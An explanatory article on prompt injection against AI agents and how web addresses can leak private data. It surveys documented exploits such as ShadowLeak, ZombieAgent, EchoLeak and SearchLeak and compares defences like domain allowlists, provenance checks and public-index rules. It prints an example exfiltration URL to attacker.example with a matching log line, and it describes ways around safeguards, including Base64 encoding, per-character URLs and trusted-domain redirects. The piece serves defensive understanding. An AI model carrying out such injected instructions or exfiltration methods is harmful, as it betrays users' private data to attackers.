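One such design uses one model to read pages and another to act. The acting model receives the user's question but never the text of a page. It might open the castle's website and request the opening hours for a Sunday in December. The reading model, which has no tools, reads the page and may return only two times of day. A hostile comment on the page could make it return the wrong times, but could not make the assistant open another site or send anything.

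The design works best when the developer can specify in advance what kind of information the reading model should return. Open-ended research is harder, because the assistant has to choose its next step partly based on what it has just read. If the reading model can return free text, it can pass the injection along. The separation also does little to protect the answer itself, which has to come from the pages anyway.

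OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), by Thomas Shadwell and Adrian Spânu, notes that early prompt injections were often plain commands, which newer models have learned to resist. The most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, in which someone uses a plausible story to get a person to do something harmful.

In 2025, outside researchers reported to OpenAI an attack email that looked like a follow-up to a meeting about a company restructuring. Along with ordinary tasks, the email contained a request to send an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system" and a statement that the assistant already had authorization. In testing, the attack worked 50% of the time when the user asked for thorough research on the day's emails.

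A filter has little to detect in such a message because it is worded like ordinary office correspondence. Shadwell and Spânu argue that the filter would have to determine whether the story is true, often without the necessary context, which is as hard as detecting a lie.

OpenAI suggests treating the assistant like a customer service employee who can grant refunds. The company expects some customers to lie and some of the lies to work, so it gives the employee rules and also uses software to limit the size of refunds and flag suspicious emails. Similarly, the developer of an AI agent looks for places where a source (a way for an outsider to influence the agent) can connect to a sink (an ability that is dangerous in the wrong context). For example, a web page is a source, and sending information to a third party is a sink. OpenAI aims to let nothing dangerous pass between them silently. If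 ChatGPT is about to send a third party something it learned in the conversation, a check called Safe Url either asks the user or blocks the transmission.

This approach is sound for leaks and unwanted actions, where a developer can identify the sink and guard it. It offers much less protection against a falsified answer, because the user is supposed to receive the answer. Software can limit a refund, but no comparable limit would prevent a wrong opening time.

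The comparison with employees is also imperfect because a con artist who fools one employee has to start again with the next, whereas copies of a model share the same weaknesses. Anthropic notes that if an attack works, sending the same email to a thousand inboxes compromises every agent that summarizes it. An attacker can also test a malicious page on the public version of a model before using it on anyone.

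Shadwell and Spânu expect a maximally intelligent model to resist social engineering better than a person would. So far, more capable models have not reliably been more resistant. In a browser test that Anthropic published in July 2026, attacks succeeded in 71 of 129 scenarios against Claude Mythos 5, then its most capable model, but in only 9 against the cheaper Claude Sonnet 5. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* criticized Anthropic for reporting Mythos 5's weaker resistance inconspicuously under a reassuring headline.

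In auto mode, Anthropic's strongest protection, probes inspect what tools return before the model acts on it, and a classifier blocks dangerous tool calls. An attack that needs a dangerous tool call has to get past both, while one that only changes the model's answer has to get past just the probes.

### Success rates in recent tests

An attack's success rate depends on the number of attempts. When Claude Opus 4.6 operated a computer through its graphical interface without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and at least one of 200 attempts succeeded 78.6% of the time (VentureBeat took both figures from Anthropic's February 2026 system card). If every attempt had the same independent chance of success, the rate would have passed 80% within ten attempts. The slower rise indicates that some scenarios were easy to break and others withstood all 200 attempts.

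The setting matters as much. In a public challenge, people sent about 6,000 emails to an assistant running on the same Opus 4.6 to try to extract a secret from it, and Willison reports that none succeeded.

Results also depend on whether the attacks are adaptive, meaning that the attacker revises them after seeing how the model responds. The table gives the share of scenarios or tasks in which at least one attempt succeeded. All the tests are from 2026, and the Claude models in the browser test used extended thinking.

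| Test | Model | Attempts | Adapted to this model | Added safeguards | Broken at least once |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Browser use, July | Claude Opus 5 | 10 | Probably not | None | 8.5% |
| Browser use, July | Claude Opus 5 | 10 | Probably not | Auto mode | 0% |
| Browser use, July | Claude Sonnet 5 | 10 | Probably not | None | 7.0% |
| Browser use, July | Claude Sonnet 5 | 10 | Probably not | Auto mode | 0% |
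| Gray Swan, September | Claude Fable 5.1 | 15 | No | None specific to injection | 1.0% |
| Gray Swan, September | GPT-6 Astra | 15 | No | On | 8.5% |
| Adaptive web attacks, October | Claude Sonnet 5 | Up to 64 | Yes | None | 30.7% |
| Adaptive web attacks, October | GPT-5.5 | Up to 64 | Yes | None | 65.2% |
| Adaptive web attacks, October | Kimi K2 | Up to 64 | Yes | None | 95.4% |

Of the companies' own tests, the July test is the closest to web browsing. Anthropic ran its models in Claude Cowork, a product that can operate a browser, and made sure they encountered the attack in each of the 129 scenarios. Auto mode stopped every attack on Opus 5. An earlier set of safeguards reduced the share of successful attacks from 8.0% to 1.4% in a browser test of Claude Opus 4.5 that allowed 100 attempts per environment, according to Anthropic.

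The July test found no failures in 129 scenarios, but the true failure rate for similar scenarios could still be about 2%. Anthropic called the test adaptive, but in September it explained that it had taken its browser attacks from tests of the older Opus 4.7 and applied them to newer models. So the attackers probably had no chance to revise their attacks against Opus 5 or auto mode. A program in each test environment checked whether the attack had succeeded, which is easier to do for an action than for a slanted answer.

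A test in which every attack fails can still miss other kinds of attack, as happened with coding agents. In a commissioned test, all 720 injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode failed. Later in August, the security researcher Johann Rehberger published an attack on auto mode that reportedly worked 80% of the time. The agent unknowingly ran a planted file rather than obeying written instructions, so the attack was not strictly prompt injection, but the test had not covered it.

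The benchmark from Gray Swan, a security company, can be used to compare developers. It covers coding, tool use and computer use, but not browsing specifically, and draws on about 1,800 attacks that people wrote in public competitions. The attacks are fixed, so the 15 attempts are not adapted in response to earlier failures. GPT-6 Astra's 8.5% was a large improvement on the 27.0% that OpenAI reported for GPT-5.6 Sol.

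Scores on this benchmark can change without any change in the model. Claude Opus 5's score rose from 2.0% in July to 4.8% in September, after Gray Swan added nine scenarios and 670 attacks.

The October figures come from Chen and colleagues, who took injections from their collection and had an automated attacker rewrite each one until it worked or 64 attempts had failed. The original injections succeeded on at most 4% of the 1,024 tasks against any of the seven models, while the rewritten ones succeeded on 31% to 95%, depending on the model. Against Sonnet 5, which had done well in Anthropic's test, the success rate rose from 2% to 31%. Few real attackers get 64 tries with full feedback on the same task, but one who rehearses in private could come close to those conditions.

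Newer models may resist these attacks better. *ANGLER* (2026), which also used an adaptive attacker, tested different types of attack planted in websites. No type succeeded more than 0.5% of the time against GPT-6.1 Sol or 2.3% of the time against Claude Sonnet 5.5. Against GPT-4o, a model from 2024, the success rates were between 29% and 42%.

In the October test, the revised attacks that aimed to change something in an application succeeded on 7.9% of tasks against Sonnet 5 and 28.5% against GPT-5.5. Those that aimed only to change the assistant's answer succeeded on 40.6% and 81.4%. Restricting an assistant to reading rules out most attacks of the first kind, which these two models already resisted fairly well, but leaves it exposed to the second.

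## How a web address can leak private data

An injected instruction can also make a read-only assistant leak private data, because even a GET request sends the server an address, and the address can contain that data.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) illustrates the problem with an address of this form:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

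Suppose a user named Maria asks an assistant to summarize a page, and a hidden instruction on the page makes the assistant open this address with her email address filled in. The fetch tool sends an ordinary GET request to `attacker.example`, and the server there adds a line like this to its log:

```
203.0.113.7 - - [04/Dec/2026:10:14:02 +0000] "GET /collect?data=maria%40example.org HTTP/1.1" 404 153
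```

The first number is the IP address of the machine that sent the request, and `%40` stands for the @ sign. The code 404 means that the server had no such page, but Maria's email address had already arrived, and the attacker can read it in the log. *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, a post on Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, shows a real log line from September 2023. Its query string contains a sharing link, apparently created through a ChatGPT plugin.

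HTTPS encryption hides the full address from outsiders in transit, but the receiving server can still read it and often logs it, as Miessler explained in *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS* (2015). OWASP's *9.3 Sensitive data does not get sent in the URL*, part of a security checklist for developers, warns that sensitive data in an address may also end up in browser histories and proxy logs.

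Removing the query string would not be enough either, because the value can also go in the path, as in `/collect/maria`, or in front of the domain name, as in `maria.attacker.example`.

### Three conditions for a leak

An attacker can make an assistant leak private data only if the assistant has access to that data, reads text that the attacker could have written, and can send information to the outside. Willison (2025) named this combination the "lethal trifecta" in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*.

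Two ordinary tools, a mailbox and a fetch tool, are enough to meet all three conditions. The mailbox supplies private data and untrusted text, because anyone can send the user an email. The fetch tool supplies more untrusted text and a way to make outside requests. Even an assistant with only a fetch tool may meet all three if the user has typed something confidential or the assistant remembers earlier conversations. Ayush Paul's attack on Claude, for example, obtained the user's name and employer without a mailbox.

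*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes the dangerous combination a little more narrowly, as untrusted text that can control an agent that can retrieve confidential data and has unrestricted outside access. On this description, a developer can reduce the risk without completely removing any of the three abilities. For example, the agent may read hostile text but usually resist it, or it may open web pages but only at a restricted set of addresses.

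Willison considers outside requests by far the easiest of the three to restrict without making an assistant much less useful. That seems right for web browsing, since an assistant that never read strangers' pages could hardly search the web. But the developer then has to find every place that can send a request, including some outside the assistant's own software.

### Where the requests come from

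| Place | What contacts the outside server | Click on a link needed? |
|---|---|---|
| Fetch tool | Usually the assistant's server | No |
| Image in an answer | The user's browser or app | No |
| Ordinary link in an answer | The user's browser | Yes |
| Link preview in a messaging app | Usually the messaging company's server | No |
| Redirect | Whichever program follows it | No further click |
| Trusted service that opens addresses on request | That service's server | No further click |

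Like a fetch tool, a search tool can leak private data through a web address if it accepts addresses as queries. Willison describes an attack on the AI agent in Notion, a note-taking product. Hidden text in a PDF made the agent put a company's client data into an address and pass that address to its search tool.

Images leak data because many chat programs display answers written in Markdown, which can include an image by giving its address. The user's browser requests the image as soon as the answer appears. Images in emails can leak data too. In May 2026 researchers showed that Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send emails to the user's own inbox without approval. When the user opened one of these emails, its images could leak download links for the user's files, and those links worked without a login.

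Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch a linked page to show its title and picture under the message. If an agent posts a link that contains private data, the app sends that data to the linked site even if the user never clicks. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* described this problem in Slack in 2024. In 2026 the security company PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an open-source personal agent, was exposed by default when people used it through Telegram (*Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*). Both apps have a setting that turns off previews for the agent's messages, but the developer or user has to know about it, because the request comes from the app rather than from the model or its fetch tool.

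Redirects get past a check that looks only at the first address. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) reported that ChatGPT's address check always approved links to bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com addresses that redirect to the real site, so anyone with a page in Bing's index had an approved link to it. Each of these addresses leads to one fixed page, so an attacker would presumably need several to spell out private data. The problem was still open when Tenable published its report. In July 2025 OpenAI told Tenable that it had improved the check, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025).

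Some trusted services open any address a visitor gives them, for example to search for similar images or create a preview. An attacker can put a second address, which points to their own server and includes the stolen data, inside an address that belongs to the service. The assistant or browser then contacts only the trusted service, which sends the data to the attacker's server when it opens the second address.

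### The image leak of 2023

Rehberger reported the image leak to Microsoft on April 8, 2023, and to OpenAI the next day. Roman Samoilenko publicly described a version for ChatGPT the same month. In that version, a website secretly added instructions to text the user copied from it and pasted into the chat, according to Willison's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (2023).

Microsoft's Bing Chat could read the page that the user had open. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* showed that a comment or advertisement on that page was enough to take control of the assistant. The assistant then displayed an image whose address contained a summary of the page and the conversation, along with any passwords on the page. The user had to start a chat but did not have to click a link. In the demonstration, the image appeared a couple of turns later, when a user might no longer connect it with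 the page.

Microsoft told Rehberger on June 15 that it had fixed the problem, although Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* later dated the fix to May. As far as Rehberger could tell, the fix relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy, which a site uses to restrict where the browser can load images and other material from. Bing Chat's policy allowed images from only four Bing addresses, so the browser no longer requested any from the attacker's server.

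Anthropic fixed the same leak in Claude, as Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* reported. OpenAI at first classified Rehberger's report as "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*.

OpenAI introduced a partial check, called url_safe, in December 2023. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web app sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, which returned whether it was safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* found that the iPhone app did not yet use the check. OpenAI did not explain how it decided which addresses were safe, and some images on Rehberger's own site still passed. He tried 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit. The check approved nine, and he used two requests to send out the word "hi".

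Private data can leak even when only nine addresses are approved. Each choice among the nine conveys about three bits of information, so a six-digit security code would take seven requests. In practice this is slow and unreliable, because requests may arrive out of order and a browser may not request an image it has already loaded. The check therefore stopped attackers from easily stealing whole conversations, but they could still extract a short secret.

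### ShadowLeak and requests from OpenAI's servers

The 2023 fixes all concerned what the user's browser or app displays, but in 2025 the security company Radware found a leak that did not involve the display. It affected Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that spends up to half an hour reading sources and then writes a report. A user could connect it to Gmail and let it browse the web in the same task, which met all three conditions.

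The email about a company restructuring, described earlier, came from this research. After reading it, Deep Research found the employee's name and home address in another message and opened a web address containing both. The user didn't click anything or see anything unusual.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes several obstacles the attack had to overcome. The agent refused plain requests to send personal data. It also treated the attacker's address as suspicious and tried to search for it online instead of opening it. When the researchers got it to open the address, it sometimes left the personal data out. The attack worked reliably when they had the agent first convert the data to Base64, which they presented to it as a security measure. Base64 turns text into a string of letters and digits that anyone can convert back. The researchers believe the encoding also got the data past a later check,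 which received only a harmless-looking string.

Radware reports a 100% success rate for this version, whereas OpenAI later reported 50% for an attack with the same email. The rates may differ because of different versions or test conditions, since Radware's advisory *ShadowLeak* (2025) says a simpler version worked about half the time. Neither company said how many attempts its figure was based on.

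The request left from OpenAI's servers, which made the leak harder to detect than the earlier ones. A company can monitor its employees' browsers and block suspicious addresses on its own network, but this request never passed through that network, so the company could not tell from its own records whether it had lost anything. The url_safe check did not help either, and Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses the agent could open directly.

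Radware reported the problem on June 18, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August. After the fix, ChatGPT would open a web address only as it had received it, without adding anything, according to Radware's *ZombieAgent*. *ZombieAgent* also describes how Radware got around that rule by late September.

### A Copilot leak through Bing

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, which can search an employee's email, calendar and company files. This time the user had to click once, on a link to Microsoft's own website. Microsoft intended the link's query string to hold a search term, but Copilot also followed instructions that an attacker put there. The private data then left through a second web address.

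The instructions made Copilot look up an email and put its title into the address of an image. Microsoft converted any HTML in a finished answer into harmless text, but the browser displayed the answer while Copilot was still writing it, so the browser requested the image before the conversion.

A Content Security Policy blocked images from unknown domains, which should still have stopped the request. But the policy allowed Bing, whose image search fetches a picture from any address it receives. The browser contacted Bing, which contacted the attacker's server with the email's title in the path.

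In the demonstration, the title contained a security code. Varonis says meeting details and private company files were also at risk, since Copilot could search everything the user had access to. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) disclosed the flaw on June 4. According to ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click*, Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers, and there were no reports of attackers using it.

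A similar leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot, EchoLeak, had become public a year earlier. Reddy and Gujral (2025) report in *EchoLeak* that the attacker only had to send an email. If Copilot read that email when the user later asked a question, it could leak internal files and messages without the user clicking anything. Here, too, the policy trusted a Microsoft service that opened outside addresses, one that creates previews for Teams. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak in May 2025 and gave it a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5.

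These cases show a weakness in lists of trusted domains. Microsoft's 2023 policy for Bing Chat had also allowed images from `www.bing.com`, the host that passed on the data in SearchLeak. A developer who lists a domain as trusted has to check every service on that domain, and Varonis recommends looking specifically for services that fetch user-supplied addresses.

### The Silent Egress experiment

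The cases above show that such leaks are possible, but not how often an attack succeeds or which defenses work best. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested both on a small scale. The eBay researchers built an agent around qwen2.5:7b, an open model with about 7 billion parameters, and ran everything on their own machines.

In each run, the user asked the agent to summarize a page. The agent automatically loaded a preview of the page, which contained an instruction to send a secret from the agent's context to the attacker's server. The researchers placed the instruction in the page's title, description, body or link text, and delivered the page either directly or through redirects. The agent was to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

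The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 runs (88%). In 95% of these, the answer to the user looked harmless, so a safety test that checked only the answers would have missed nearly all the leaks. The agent did not contact the server in any of the 120 further runs with harmless pages.

Splitting the secret made the leak harder to spot in any single request. The share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data fell from 96.7% to 26.3%. Part of the drop came from failed attacks. The agent contacted the attacker in 238 of 240 runs when it had to send the secret whole, but in only 185 of 240 when it had to split it. Lan and colleagues don't report how often all four pieces arrived.

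The 73% is also less exact than it looks. The researchers calculated the same measure for the first three requests together and got 15.8%. By their own definition, that figure cannot be lower than the 73% for the first request alone, so they must have calculated at least one of the two some other way.

They then tested defenses against the simplest attack, with the instruction in the body of the page and the secret sent whole. Each row of the table covers 30 runs.

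| Defense | Agent tried to send the secret | Request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the developer's instructions | 67% | 67% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 57% | 57% |
| List of allowed domains | 100% | 0% |
| Block on suspicious addresses | 83% | 0% |
| Block on words such as "password" | 23% | 0% |
| Block on random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

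The list of allowed domains gave the clearest result, because the agent tried to send the secret every time and the software stopped it every time. The block on suspicious addresses also let no secrets through, but this is weaker evidence. It rejected any path containing the word "collect", which appears in the attack addresses printed in the paper, and an attacker could avoid that rule by choosing another word.

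The last two rows are hard to explain. A filter that checks a finished request should not affect how often the model tries to send one, yet the attempts fell to 23% and then to none. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking values while the filter was active, but don't explain how information about the filter could have reached it. The filter blocked values of more than ten characters whose Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, exceeded 4 bits per character. The sample key printed in the paper has an entropy of about 3.85, so the filter would have let it through.

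The researchers did not test these filters on split secrets, but the entropy filter would have missed them because each piece in their example has only four characters.

The 88% figure is limited evidence about commercial assistants, partly because the model tested, Qwen2.5:7b, was small even when it came out in 2024. The test also favored the attacker because the secret was already in the context, the developer's instructions covered little more than how to use the tools, and nothing cleaned the web page before the model read it. Lan and colleagues argue that stronger models might do worse because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. ShadowLeak shows that a much more capable system could also fail, but GPT-6.1 Sol resisted nearly every attack in the ANGLER tests described earlier.

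The results for warnings and tags depend just as much on this model, since both work only if the model heeds them. The result for allowed domains should apply better to other models, because the software blocks a forbidden address whichever model wrote it. However, this protects the data only if no allowed domain forwards requests elsewhere, as Bing did for Copilot.

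## Rules on which addresses an assistant may open

Commercial assistants use several rules to limit which addresses the model can open. The loosest is a list of allowed domains, which restricts only the site an address belongs to. Stricter rules apply to the whole address, and under the strictest, the assistant never contacts the site.

Every rule below can stop the request that would send Maria's email address to `attacker.example`. The rules differ in what a more patient attacker can still learn and in how many harmless pages they block.

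### Lists of trusted domains

With a domain list, the software checks whether the host in the web address is on the list. If it is, the software sends the request. Otherwise, the model gets an error. `attacker.example` is not on the list, so its server never receives Maria's email address.

In the fetch tool that Anthropic offers to developers, an entry for `example.com` in a list of allowed or blocked domains also covers `docs.example.com` and every other subdomain, according to Anthropic's *Server tools*. Allowing all subdomains is convenient for a company's own site but risky for a hosting service that gives each customer a subdomain, because an attacker may be one of the customers. The tool compares only domains, so an entry with a path, such as `example.com/blog`, never matches anything. A developer therefore cannot allow just one part of a site, and trying to block one part blocks nothing.

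An older version of Anthropic's documentation also warned about look-alike letters. A domain spelled with a Cyrillic "а" can look identical to `amazon.com`. A character-by-character comparison tells the two apart, but a developer who pastes the wrong one into the list will not see the mistake.

Redirects, such as the Bing links in ChatGPT, are the best-known way around a list that is applied only to the first address. A list can also fail without a redirect.

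Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, could fetch pages without user approval from `huggingface.co`, where anyone can publish AI models. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) describes how an attacker could upload models there and get the agent to request their files. Hugging Face counted these requests as downloads, so a pattern of requests could leak private data through the download counts without the agent contacting a server that the attacker owned. Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 2.1.163.

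Claude Cowork had a similar problem with Anthropic's own API, which was on its list of approved domains because the product cannot work without it. Hidden instructions in a file made Claude upload the user's other files to that API, using a key from the attacker's Anthropic account. The software let the files through because the domain was approved. Anthropic now accepts only requests that carry the session's own token. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* concludes that an entry on such a list is a "capability grant", because it permits every function reachable on that domain.

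A domain list therefore suits an assistant with a narrow job, such as answering questions from one company's manuals. Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, thought developers could safely build on a fetch tool if they limited it to domains that cannot leak data, but warned that such domains are tricky to find. For a general assistant, a short list would block most of the web, and a long one would allow many functions that nobody has checked.

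### Asking the user

The software can show an unknown address to the user and send the request only if the user agrees, instead of refusing to open it. OpenAI uses a dialog that displays the address, warns that the link is not verified and may share data from the conversation, and lets the user copy or open the link.

Maria would probably notice her own email address in the query string. She would be less likely to recognize it in Base64, the encoding used in ShadowLeak, and a web address that ends in a single letter looks harmless.

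Anthropic also found that people paid less attention to each permission prompt as the number of prompts grew. It reports that users of Claude Code approved about 93% of prompts, which covered commands and file changes as well as network access. Most of these requests were presumably fine, so the figure does not show how many approvals were mistakes. Anthropic responded to the loss of attention with a sandbox, a closed-off environment with no network access by default, in which the agent can work without asking. This cut the number of prompts by 84%.

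Approval does not help if an attacker has already convinced the user. In a February 2026 exercise at Anthropic, a researcher emailed an employee a ready-made prompt, and the employee ran it in Claude Code. The prompt mixed routine setup steps with an instruction to send the employee's cloud login keys to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 repeat attempts. Anthropic concluded that only limits on network traffic and file access would have stopped it.

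Asking therefore works best as an exception, after another rule has cleared the ordinary pages.

### Addresses already in the conversation

Anthropic released its fetch tool for developers in September 2025 with a rule that Claude may not make up addresses. When Claude requests a page, the software does roughly the following:

1. It looks for that exact address earlier in the conversation.
2. It accepts the address if it came from the user's message, a search result, an earlier fetch or one of the developer's own tools.
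3. It refuses the address if it appears only in text that Claude wrote.

In Maria's case, Claude had to put her email address into the link, so the finished link did not appear earlier and the tool blocks it. This happens whether or not Claude encoded the email address, and however persuasive the hidden instruction was. Willison tested the consumer version of Claude and found the same limit.

This restriction is a fairly small inconvenience for the user. Claude can open any search result and any link that the user pastes. It cannot correct a mistyped address or change `month=december` to `month=january` in the castle's link, unless the new address appears in a search result or on a page. The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters.

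The rule depends on each part of the conversation being labelled with its true source. Willison pointed out at launch that many developers paste emails or documents into what their software sends as the user's message. Any address in that text then counts as the user's own. An attacker who gets an address accepted this way still can't make Claude add data to it, but if several are accepted, the attacker can learn something from which of them Claude opens.

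### Addresses already in a public index

In January 2026 OpenAI described a rule based on where an address came from. If an address was already public, independently of any user's conversation, it is much less likely to contain that user's private data. The check has four steps:

1. A crawler with no access to conversations or accounts records addresses that it finds on the public web.
2. When ChatGPT is about to open a page or load an image, the software looks up the exact address in that record.
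3. If the address is there, ChatGPT loads it automatically.
4. If not, the software tells the model to try another site or shows the user the warning described above.

Addresses that the user types also appear to count as safe for the rest of the chat, according to Johann Rehberger's Embrace The Red post on OpenAI's accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

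The rule works only if the index is independent of ChatGPT's own traffic. If the index also included addresses from that traffic, the link with Maria's email address could be added after one attempt and be allowed on the next.

This rule handles redirects much better than a domain list does. To send data through a trusted site's redirect, the model has to put the attacker's address, including the data, in the trusted site's query string. Nobody has published that combined address, so it is not in the index. An attacker's indexed page can redirect anywhere, but the redirect can carry only information the attacker already has.

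OpenAI's check is also stricter than Anthropic's about new addresses. Anthropic's tool may accept an address that a site created seconds ago, as long as it appeared in an accepted source. OpenAI's check requires the crawler to have found the address earlier, so an attacker cannot create a new one for each victim.

The rule also prevents the assistant from automatically opening some harmless pages. These presumably include pages too new for the crawler to have visited, unlisted documents, and results from a site's own search box, whose addresses contain the user's search terms. The assistant can still offer links to these pages, but the user has to open them.

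OpenAI promises only to prevent the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". An indexed page may still contain false information or hidden instructions. Rehberger also worries that the check won't be applied everywhere, because every team at OpenAI has to remember to use it. The 2023 check, for example, was missing from the macOS and iPhone apps.

### Stored pages only

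In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT makes no live requests for web pages and can read only copies that OpenAI has already stored. OpenAI introduced the mode for organizations in February 2026 and began extending it to personal accounts in June.

In Lockdown Mode, no live browsing requests leave OpenAI's network, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026). An attacker therefore cannot use server logs to see which stored page ChatGPT opened, as long as opening a stored page never triggers a fetch of a fresh copy.

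This protection significantly limits what ChatGPT can do. The castle's holiday hours may be out of date, and regular answers may not show images. Deep Research, agent mode and file downloads for data analysis are unavailable. The user can switch Lockdown Mode off for a single chat, which makes it more convenient but also easier to forget. OpenAI originally recommended it for a small group, such as executives and security teams, and said most users did not need it.

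OpenAI's current help page, *Lockdown Mode*, says the setting does not affect network access in Codex, the company's coding agent. In workspaces managed by an organization, connected apps also keep working unless an administrator disables them. OpenAI advises against letting ChatGPT write through an app, even a trusted one, if the administrator cannot be sure who will see the result. It does not guarantee that the setting prevents all leaks, and it warns that a hidden instruction in a stored page or uploaded file can still make an answer wrong.

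### What a choice of address reveals

The rules that allow live requests all let an attacker learn private data from the order in which the assistant opens permitted addresses. Suppose an attacker has 36 addresses that pass the check, one for each letter and digit. If a hidden instruction makes the assistant open the address for "m", then the one for "a" and so on, the attacker can read Maria's name in the server's log, even though the assistant never wrote anything into an address.

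Information theory measures in bits how much such a choice reveals. One bit is the information in the answer to a yes-or-no question whose two answers are equally likely, and a choice among N equally likely options carries log₂ N bits. If the attacker can observe requests to N addresses, one fetch reveals up to log₂ N bits, which is about 5.17 bits for N = 36. Twelve fetches have 36¹² possible sequences, so they can reveal up to 12 × 5.17, or about 62 bits. If the developer caps fetches at five, the maximum falls to about 26 bits.

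Rehberger suggested two related limits in his post on Embrace The Red. The developer could store each response for a few minutes, so that a second request for the same address never reaches the site, or forbid the agent to open the same address twice in a session. Under the second limit, the agent has 36 options for the first fetch, 35 for the next, and 25 for the twelfth. Multiplying all twelve numbers gives the number of possible sequences, and its base-2 logarithm is about 59 bits, only three fewer than if repeats were allowed.

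Hiding the order from the attacker helps much more, for example by having the requests all arrive at once and in no reliable sequence. The attacker then learns only which 12 of the 36 addresses the assistant opened. Each set of 12 could have come in 12! orders, so this reduces the total by log₂ 12!, or about 29 bits, to about 30 bits.

| Fetches from 36 addresses | Repeats allowed, order visible | No repeats, order visible | No repeats, order hidden |
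|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5.2 bits | 5.2 bits | 5.2 bits |
| 5 | 25.8 bits | 25.4 bits | 18.5 bits |
| 12 | 62.0 bits | 59.1 bits | 30.2 bits |

For comparison, a random six-digit security code contains about 20 bits and a random ten-digit number about 33. A cap of five fetches doesn't protect the six-digit code if an attacker can get the model to convert it first. Spelling out the code one digit at a time takes six fetches, but four fetches with 36 options each can distinguish 36⁴, or almost 1.7 million, values, which is more than the million possible codes.

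Rehberger notes that a larger blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, and that an attacker could extend the method to thousands. With 10,000 indexed pages, a single fetch could reveal any four-digit PIN.

Doubling the number of addresses an assistant may open adds only one bit to what each fetch can leak, while doubling the number of fetches doubles the total. Capping fetches is therefore more effective than limiting addresses, but it hinders research questions that need dozens of pages. Anthropic's fetch tool has no default cap. Developers can set one, but it applies only to a single turn, so a leak could continue after the user's next message.

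### ZombieAgent

Radware used this weakness against ChatGPT. After ShadowLeak, OpenAI had forbidden ChatGPT to add anything to an address it received. The researchers therefore put complete addresses in an email, one for each letter and digit and one for the space. When the user later asked ChatGPT for help with Gmail, it read the email, found the private information and opened the address for each character in turn, which the rule did not prevent because ChatGPT never altered an address.

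To keep the characters in order, the researchers added a separate address for each character in each position. A 12-character text of only letters and digits would need 12 × 36 = 432 addresses. The assistant opens each address at most once, so this version would also get past a ban on repeat visits. The attacker could reassemble the text even if the requests arrived out of order, and would therefore receive all 62 bits.

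The demonstrations focused on Gmail, but Radware warned that the method could also expose data from services such as Outlook, Google Drive and GitHub, along with the user's chat history and stored memories. In one version, an attacker used a shared file to add instructions to ChatGPT's memory, and the leak continued in later chats. OpenAI had tried to prevent this by blocking memory once a chat had used a connected service, but the researchers found that ChatGPT could still read its memory first and then use the service.

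Radware reported the problem on September 26, 2025, OpenAI fixed it on December 16, and Radware published it in January 2026. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link appears in a well-known public index or the user supplied it. An attacker can therefore no longer use newly invented addresses on a new domain. The same method should still work in principle if the attacker has enough pages in the index, as OpenAI acknowledges in its own paper.

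### Ayush Paul's chain of links

Until July 2026, Anthropic's rule allowed Claude to open links that it found in pages it had already fetched. This was useful for long documents split across several pages, but it also let a site supply Claude with new addresses at every step.

Paul's site offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for the hyphen. Each link led to a page with 27 more, whose addresses were one character longer. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how Claude followed these links to spell out the user's name, employer and home city from its memory of earlier conversations.

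A choice among 27 links carries 4.75 bits. *The Read-Only Lie*, by dyb, estimates that the attack needed about 30 fetches and so could carry about 143 bits in one turn. It also notes that Claude inferred Paul's home city from the name of a high school hackathon, although Paul had never stated it directly. A user who checks the stored memories for sensitive facts may therefore underestimate what an attacker could learn.

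The address grew at each step until it contained the whole word, so neither banning repeat visits nor hiding the order of visits would have helped. OpenAI's index rule would have blocked this version, because nobody could publish an address in advance for each of the about 200 trillion possible ten-character strings of letters and hyphens. The attacker would have had to go back to a fixed set of addresses, as in ZombieAgent.

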